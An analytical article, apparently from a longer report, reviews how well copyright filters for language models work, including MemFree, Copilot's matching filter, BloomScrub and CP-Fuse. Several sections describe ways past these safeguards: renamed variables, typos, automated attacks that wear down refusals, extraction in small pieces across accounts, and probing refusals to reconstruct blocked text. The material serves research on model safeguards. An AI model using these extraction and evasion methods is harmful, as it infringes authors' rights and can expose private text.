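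A Bloom filter of all ten-token runs in a dataset of about 800 gigabytes took up 40.5 gigabytes. Ippolito and colleagues cut this to 1.6 gigabytes by storing only runs that occurred repeatedly, because models are more likely to memorise those. The smaller filter gives weaker copyright protection. It never misses a run it has stored, but it would leave out much of a book that appears only once in the training data.

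### Near copies

Suppose a model reproduces a 1,000-word passage but changes every tenth word. A filter that looks for matching ten-word runs finds none, because any ten consecutive words include a changed one, although 900 of the words are the same. A filter that replaces words can create such a copy by letting nine words through and changing the tenth, after which the model may return to the original.

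Ippolito and colleagues found that memorised text got past the MemFree filter when their models added spelling mistakes, changed punctuation or wrote "&" for "and". MemFree made the output less similar to the training text on average, but some passages remained close copies. Without any filter, the team found up to twice as many memorised passages with a looser measure of similarity as with exact matching. They warn that the looser measure can both overcount and undercount.

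The team also tested the filter in GitHub Copilot, a programming assistant separate from Microsoft 365 Copilot. The filter blocked a famous function from the computer game *Quake*. But when the surrounding code used French variable names, Copilot wrote the same function with French names, and the filter let it through. Even without special prompting, Copilot also produced copies that passed the filter because of changed capitals, altered spacing or small mistakes.

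Those models are long out of date, but in later tests MemFree still let some copying through, and it also reduced quality. *Copyright-Protected Language Generation via Adaptive Model Fusion* (Abad, Donhauser and colleagues, 2024) reports that MemFree lowered the share of programming problems a model solved from 43% to 32%, because changing one word can rename a variable or alter a program's logic. Ippolito and colleagues had found no effect on performance. The results may differ because Abad and colleagues had made their models memorise heavily, which gave the filter more to block.

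### How GitHub Copilot handles matching code

GitHub introduced Copilot's filter in June 2022. According to GitHub's *Preview* (2022), the filter blocked suggestions of 150 or more characters that matched public code, ignoring spaces and line breaks. The current version compares each suggestion, along with roughly 150 characters of surrounding code, against an index of GitHub's public repositories. The index leaves out private repositories and code hosted elsewhere, and it can miss recent code because GitHub refreshes it only every few months.

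Users can block or allow matching suggestions. According to GitHub, Copilot's "Block" setting hides a suggestion if there is "a match, or a near match". The documentation does not define a near match, so it's unclear whether the filter would now catch the *Quake* function with French names.

With "Allow", Copilot shows the suggestion. If the programmer accepts it, Copilot logs the address of each matching file and any licence GitHub found for it. The programmer can then credit the author, follow the licence or delete the code. This option suits software because many software licences permit copying on conditions such as attribution, while few novels have such a licence.

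A match does not prove where the code came from. GitHub suggests testing the feature by asking for commonly used code. Its sample log lists a GPL-3.0-licensed file containing FizzBuzz, a beginners' exercise that many programmers have written independently. The listed repository may also have copied the code from elsewhere.

GitHub says matches typically occur in less than 1% of Copilot's suggestions. For a programmer who sees 100 suggestions a day, that could still mean nearly one match a day. Copilot doesn't check code that the programmer wrote or suggestions that the programmer has altered.

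Blocking is not available in every product. GitHub's *Copilot coding agent supports code referencing* (2026) explains that the coding agent, which works on tasks by itself, ignores the "Block" setting and only highlights matches in its session logs. GitHub's policy table lists two Copilot products that can only annotate matches. A company that chooses "Block" therefore still needs someone to read the agent's logs, especially if its indemnity depends on using the filter.

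### Refusal training

Developers also train models to refuse requests for long protected passages and perhaps offer a summary instead. This approach doesn't need a list of protected works, and the model can take the request into account. For example, it can quote one line for a student's essay but decline to recite the chapter. However, the text stays in the model's weights.

Ahmed and colleagues had to get past refusals from two of the four commercial models they tested. For the first Harry Potter novel, their automated attack needed 258 attempts with Claude 3.7 Sonnet and 5,179 with GPT-4.1. Refusal training therefore made extraction slower and more expensive but did not prevent it. Fine-tuning can also make a model less likely to refuse.

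A rule in the system prompt takes almost no effort to add, but it did little to prevent copying in tests on models that had memorised their training text. Abad and colleagues suggest that fine-tuning may have overridden the model's safety training.

### Rewriting copied passages

Zhang, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *Certified Mitigation of Worst-Case LLM Copyright Infringement*, use a Bloom filter to find copied passages and a second model to reword them. Their system, BloomScrub, works in four steps:

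1. A program stores every run of 25 characters from the protected texts in a Bloom filter, ignoring differences in capitals, spacing and punctuation.
2. It checks the finished answer and joins overlapping matches into longer quotations. For example, 26 consecutive matches make a quotation of 50 characters.
3. If a quotation is too long, the second model gets the answer and a list of the copied passages, and rewrites it.
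4. The program checks the new version and repeats the process up to a fixed number of times. If a long quotation remains, the system can withhold the answer.

Ignoring capitalization and spacing fixes some of the weaknesses that Ippolito and colleagues found. A single false match also does little harm, because detecting a long quotation requires many matches in a row.

Zhang and colleagues fine-tuned an eight-billion-parameter Llama model on news articles, then gave it the beginning of each article and let it continue. The table shows the length in characters of the longest match with the real continuation, and a score for answering factual questions about the articles. R-CAD is an earlier method that looks up the protected article and steers the model away from its wording.

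| Method | Longest match, *New York Times* | Longest match, CNN and Daily Mail | Factual score, *New York Times* | Factual score, CNN and Daily Mail |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 542 | 314 | 47.9% | 27.7% |
| System prompt | 542 | 575 | 44.2% | 27.4% |
| MemFree | 73 | 164 | 45.0% | 25.8% |
| R-CAD | 291 | 218 | 47.9% | 27.7% |
| BloomScrub | 54 | 50 | 47.8% | 27.7% |

The system prompt did not shorten the longest match on either set of articles. The increase from 314 to 575 may be due to chance, because each figure comes from a single worst answer. R-CAD kept its factual score, but its output sometimes contained run-together or made-up words.

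Without protection, around 20% of answers contained a quotation of more than 100 characters from the collection, compared with at most 0.1% with BloomScrub. Quotations of more than 50 characters remained in 10.9% of answers based on the *New York Times* and 5.6% of the others. Only withholding answers brought these figures to zero, and "certified" in the paper's title refers to this step. To get the guarantee for the *New York Times*, a company would have to refuse about one answer in nine. Some of those refusals would be pointless, because a name such as "the Fundamentalist Church of Jesus Christ of Latter-day Saints", at 62 characters, exceeds the 50-character limit by itself.

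Each rewrite means running a model again, and stricter limits require more rewrites. Withholding answers also lowered the average relevance score for the *New York Times* from 2.9 to 2.6 out of 5.

Rewording a passage may not solve the legal problem, because a close paraphrase can still be substantially similar to the original. The system could even make copying harder to detect by changing just enough words to pass its own filter. Zhang and colleagues acknowledge that the problem of copying without exact quotation remains unsolved.

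### Near access-freeness

Instead of checking text against a list, Vyas, Kakade and Barak (2023), in *On Provable Copyright Protection for Generative Models*, propose a guarantee about the model's probabilities. In US law, a claimant has to show that the defendant had access to the work as well as that the two texts are similar. Vyas and colleagues therefore compare a model with a "safe" one that was trained without the work. They call a model k-near access-free if, for every prompt x and every protected work C:

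```
Δ( p(·|x) ‖ safe_C(·|x) ) ≤ k
```

Here p is the model, safe_C is the model trained without C, and Δ measures in bits how far apart their probabilities are. In the strictest version, Δ is the base-2 logarithm of the largest ratio between the probabilities that p and safe_C give to the same output. The definition then limits the chance of copying:

```
P(p copies C) ≤ 2^k × P(safe_C copies C)
```

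If k is 10, the model is at most 1,024 times as likely to copy the work as a model that never saw it. If that model's chance of copying the work is one in a trillion, the first model's chance is at most about one in a billion.

A developer builds such a model by splitting the training data in two, with each protected work in only one half, and training a model on each half. The combined model assigns every possible answer the lower of the two models' probabilities, then rescales these values so that they add up to 1. Suppose one model reproduces a page of the cookbook half the time and the other, which was not trained on the book, practically never does. The combined model then practically never reproduces the page, but it keeps the general cooking advice that both models give.

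### Combining models with CP-Fuse

Calculating these probabilities for every possible answer is impractical, so Vyas and colleagues suggest combining the models one token at a time. CP-Fuse, the method of Abad and colleagues, improves on this version. It chooses the probability of each next token with the formula:

```
log p = α log p1 + β log p2 + γ
```

The weights α and β set the influence of the two models, and γ makes the probabilities add up to 1. CP-Fuse adjusts the weights as it generates text. If the text so far is much more probable under the first model, that model may be reproducing something the second was not trained on, so CP-Fuse gives the second more weight. The earlier method, CP-Δ, keeps the weights equal, so the output can start reproducing a passage that one model memorised and continue with it.

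Abad and colleagues tested this on models with seven billion parameters. They trained each model on 3,000 examples, going through the full set 50 times so that the model would memorise them. The table gives the average length, in characters, of exact matches in the worst 5% of outputs, for one half of the data.

| Method | Python code | Mathematics abstracts | Stories |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 1,470 | 1,398 | 1,316 |
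| System prompt | 1,361 | 1,023 | 1,118 |
| MemFree | 165 | 111 | 64 |
| CP-Δ | 273 | 342 | 37 |
| CP-Fuse | 70 | 56 | 28 |
| Model trained only on the other half | 43 | 42 | 26 |

The last row shows how much overlap occurs without memorisation. CP-Fuse nearly reached that level for stories but not for code. The paper's claim that CP-Fuse shortened matches more than 25-fold holds for abstracts and stories, but the reduction for code was about 21-fold.

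CP-Fuse hardly reduced the quality of the output. Models using it solved 47% of one set of programming problems, compared with about 43% without protection. Stories scored 2.17 out of 5 for fluency both with and without CP-Fuse, but 1.70 with MemFree. However, CP-Fuse runs two models, which roughly doubles the computation for each token.

CP-Fuse depends on keeping each work in only one half of the training data, which is hard for popular books because reviews, fan sites and pirated copies repeat their text. If both models have memorised a passage, combining them does not suppress it. CP-Fuse may therefore work worst for the books that are easiest to extract. Abad and colleagues acknowledge that the method relies on this separation and recommend tests with larger models and real books or songs.

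### Where the guarantee fails

Cohen (2025), in *Blameless Users in a Clean Room*, proves that a near access-free model can still let users copy training text word for word. The definition limits what each answer can reveal to k bits, but a user can combine answers from several prompts. A single prompt containing only a work's unprotected ideas can also be enough. Cohen built the models in these proofs to make the guarantee fail, and accepts that it may still help in many ordinary situations.

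Cohen's alternative, clean-room protection, covers users who would be unlikely to copy a work if the model had been trained without it. Training with differential privacy can provide this protection, but only if no protected work appears more than once in the data, even within other works. Meeting that condition requires the same difficult separation of sources.

Courts also do not use closeness between two models as a test. Vyas and colleagues say it is unclear how far courts will accept their approach. Cohen quotes three legal and technical researchers who object that "you would have copied the work from somewhere else" is no defence. If the safe model learned the cookbook page from an unauthorised copy on another website, both models would reproduce it and the comparison would not reveal the copying.

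Elkin-Koren, Hacohen and colleagues (2023) argue in *Can Copyright be Reduced to Privacy?* that such measures are too broad, because they restrict a work's content when copyright protects only its expression, and too narrow, because they miss expression that reaches the model through another work. Cohen agrees that copyright cannot be reduced to privacy, but replies that neither proposal is meant to do this. The mathematics limits one risk under stated conditions, as a security proof in cryptography does.

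The guarantee also covers only output. Vyas and colleagues note that a model could satisfy it even if its weights encoded the entire training set. The guarantee would not have helped OpenAI in Munich, where the court treated lyrics stored in the model as copies.

### Which text to protect

Copyright protects an original work as soon as someone writes it down, usually without registration, so no complete list of protected works exists. A filter covers only the works its developer has obtained, so it will miss most blog posts, unpublished manuscripts and translations.

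If a developer instead put all of the training data into the filter, it would also block Shakespeare and open-source licences that programmers are supposed to reproduce exactly. A Bloom filter cannot identify which work matched, so the developer can't check whether that work is out of copyright or covered by a licence agreement. Removing a work from an ordinary Bloom filter also risks missing matches with other works, because they may share its bits. The developer therefore has to rebuild the filter when a copyright expires or a publisher grants a licence, unless each publisher has a separate one.

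Even with a perfect list, a filter could not separate lawful quotation from unlawful copying, because the same 100 words might be lawful in a review of a novel and unlawful in a free substitute for it. Zhang and colleagues tested limits of 50 and 100 characters, and GitHub uses about 150, but copyright law sets no general length below which copying is always allowed.

### Streamed answers and copying in pieces

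Most chatbots display an answer while the model is still generating it. A filter that detects a copy only after 50 matching words lets the reader see the first 49, unless the application holds back the most recent words. At 50 words a second, holding them back would delay the text by about a second. BloomScrub needs the complete answer before it can start, so users would wait much longer.

A filter that permits short quotations can also let a whole book through in pieces. If it allowed 40 words per reply, a user could collect an 80,000-word novel in 2,000 replies. Ahmed and colleagues extracted books by repeatedly asking models to continue, although the models wrote far more than 40 words at a time. An application could limit how much of each book a user receives, but it would need to identify the book, which a Bloom filter can't do, and keep a record of what every user has read. Even then,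 a user could get around the limit by opening several accounts.

### Refusals that reveal what they protect

If a chatbot blocks only text that matches its store of protected text, a user can test whether a paragraph is in the store by supplying it and asking the chatbot to repeat it. If the chatbot refuses, the paragraph is probably protected. If the filter contains the training data, the refusal also suggests that the model was trained on that paragraph. This could help an author who suspects that a company used a book without permission, but it could also expose private material, such as a customer's unpublished manuscript.

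A filter can even help someone reconstruct the text it blocks. A person who knows four words of a five-word run can try different fifth words, and the one the filter blocks is probably correct. False alarms make this less certain, but the person can check a guess by testing the next run.

Hiding the reason for a refusal helps only if the chatbot also refuses for other reasons. Otherwise, the user can still infer that there was a match. Replacing a word instead of blocking the answer also leaves a clue, because the chatbot never produces the original phrase. Developers can slow down guessing by limiting repeated requests that differ by only a word or two. Filling the filter only with published works is safer, and private text should also stay out of the training data.
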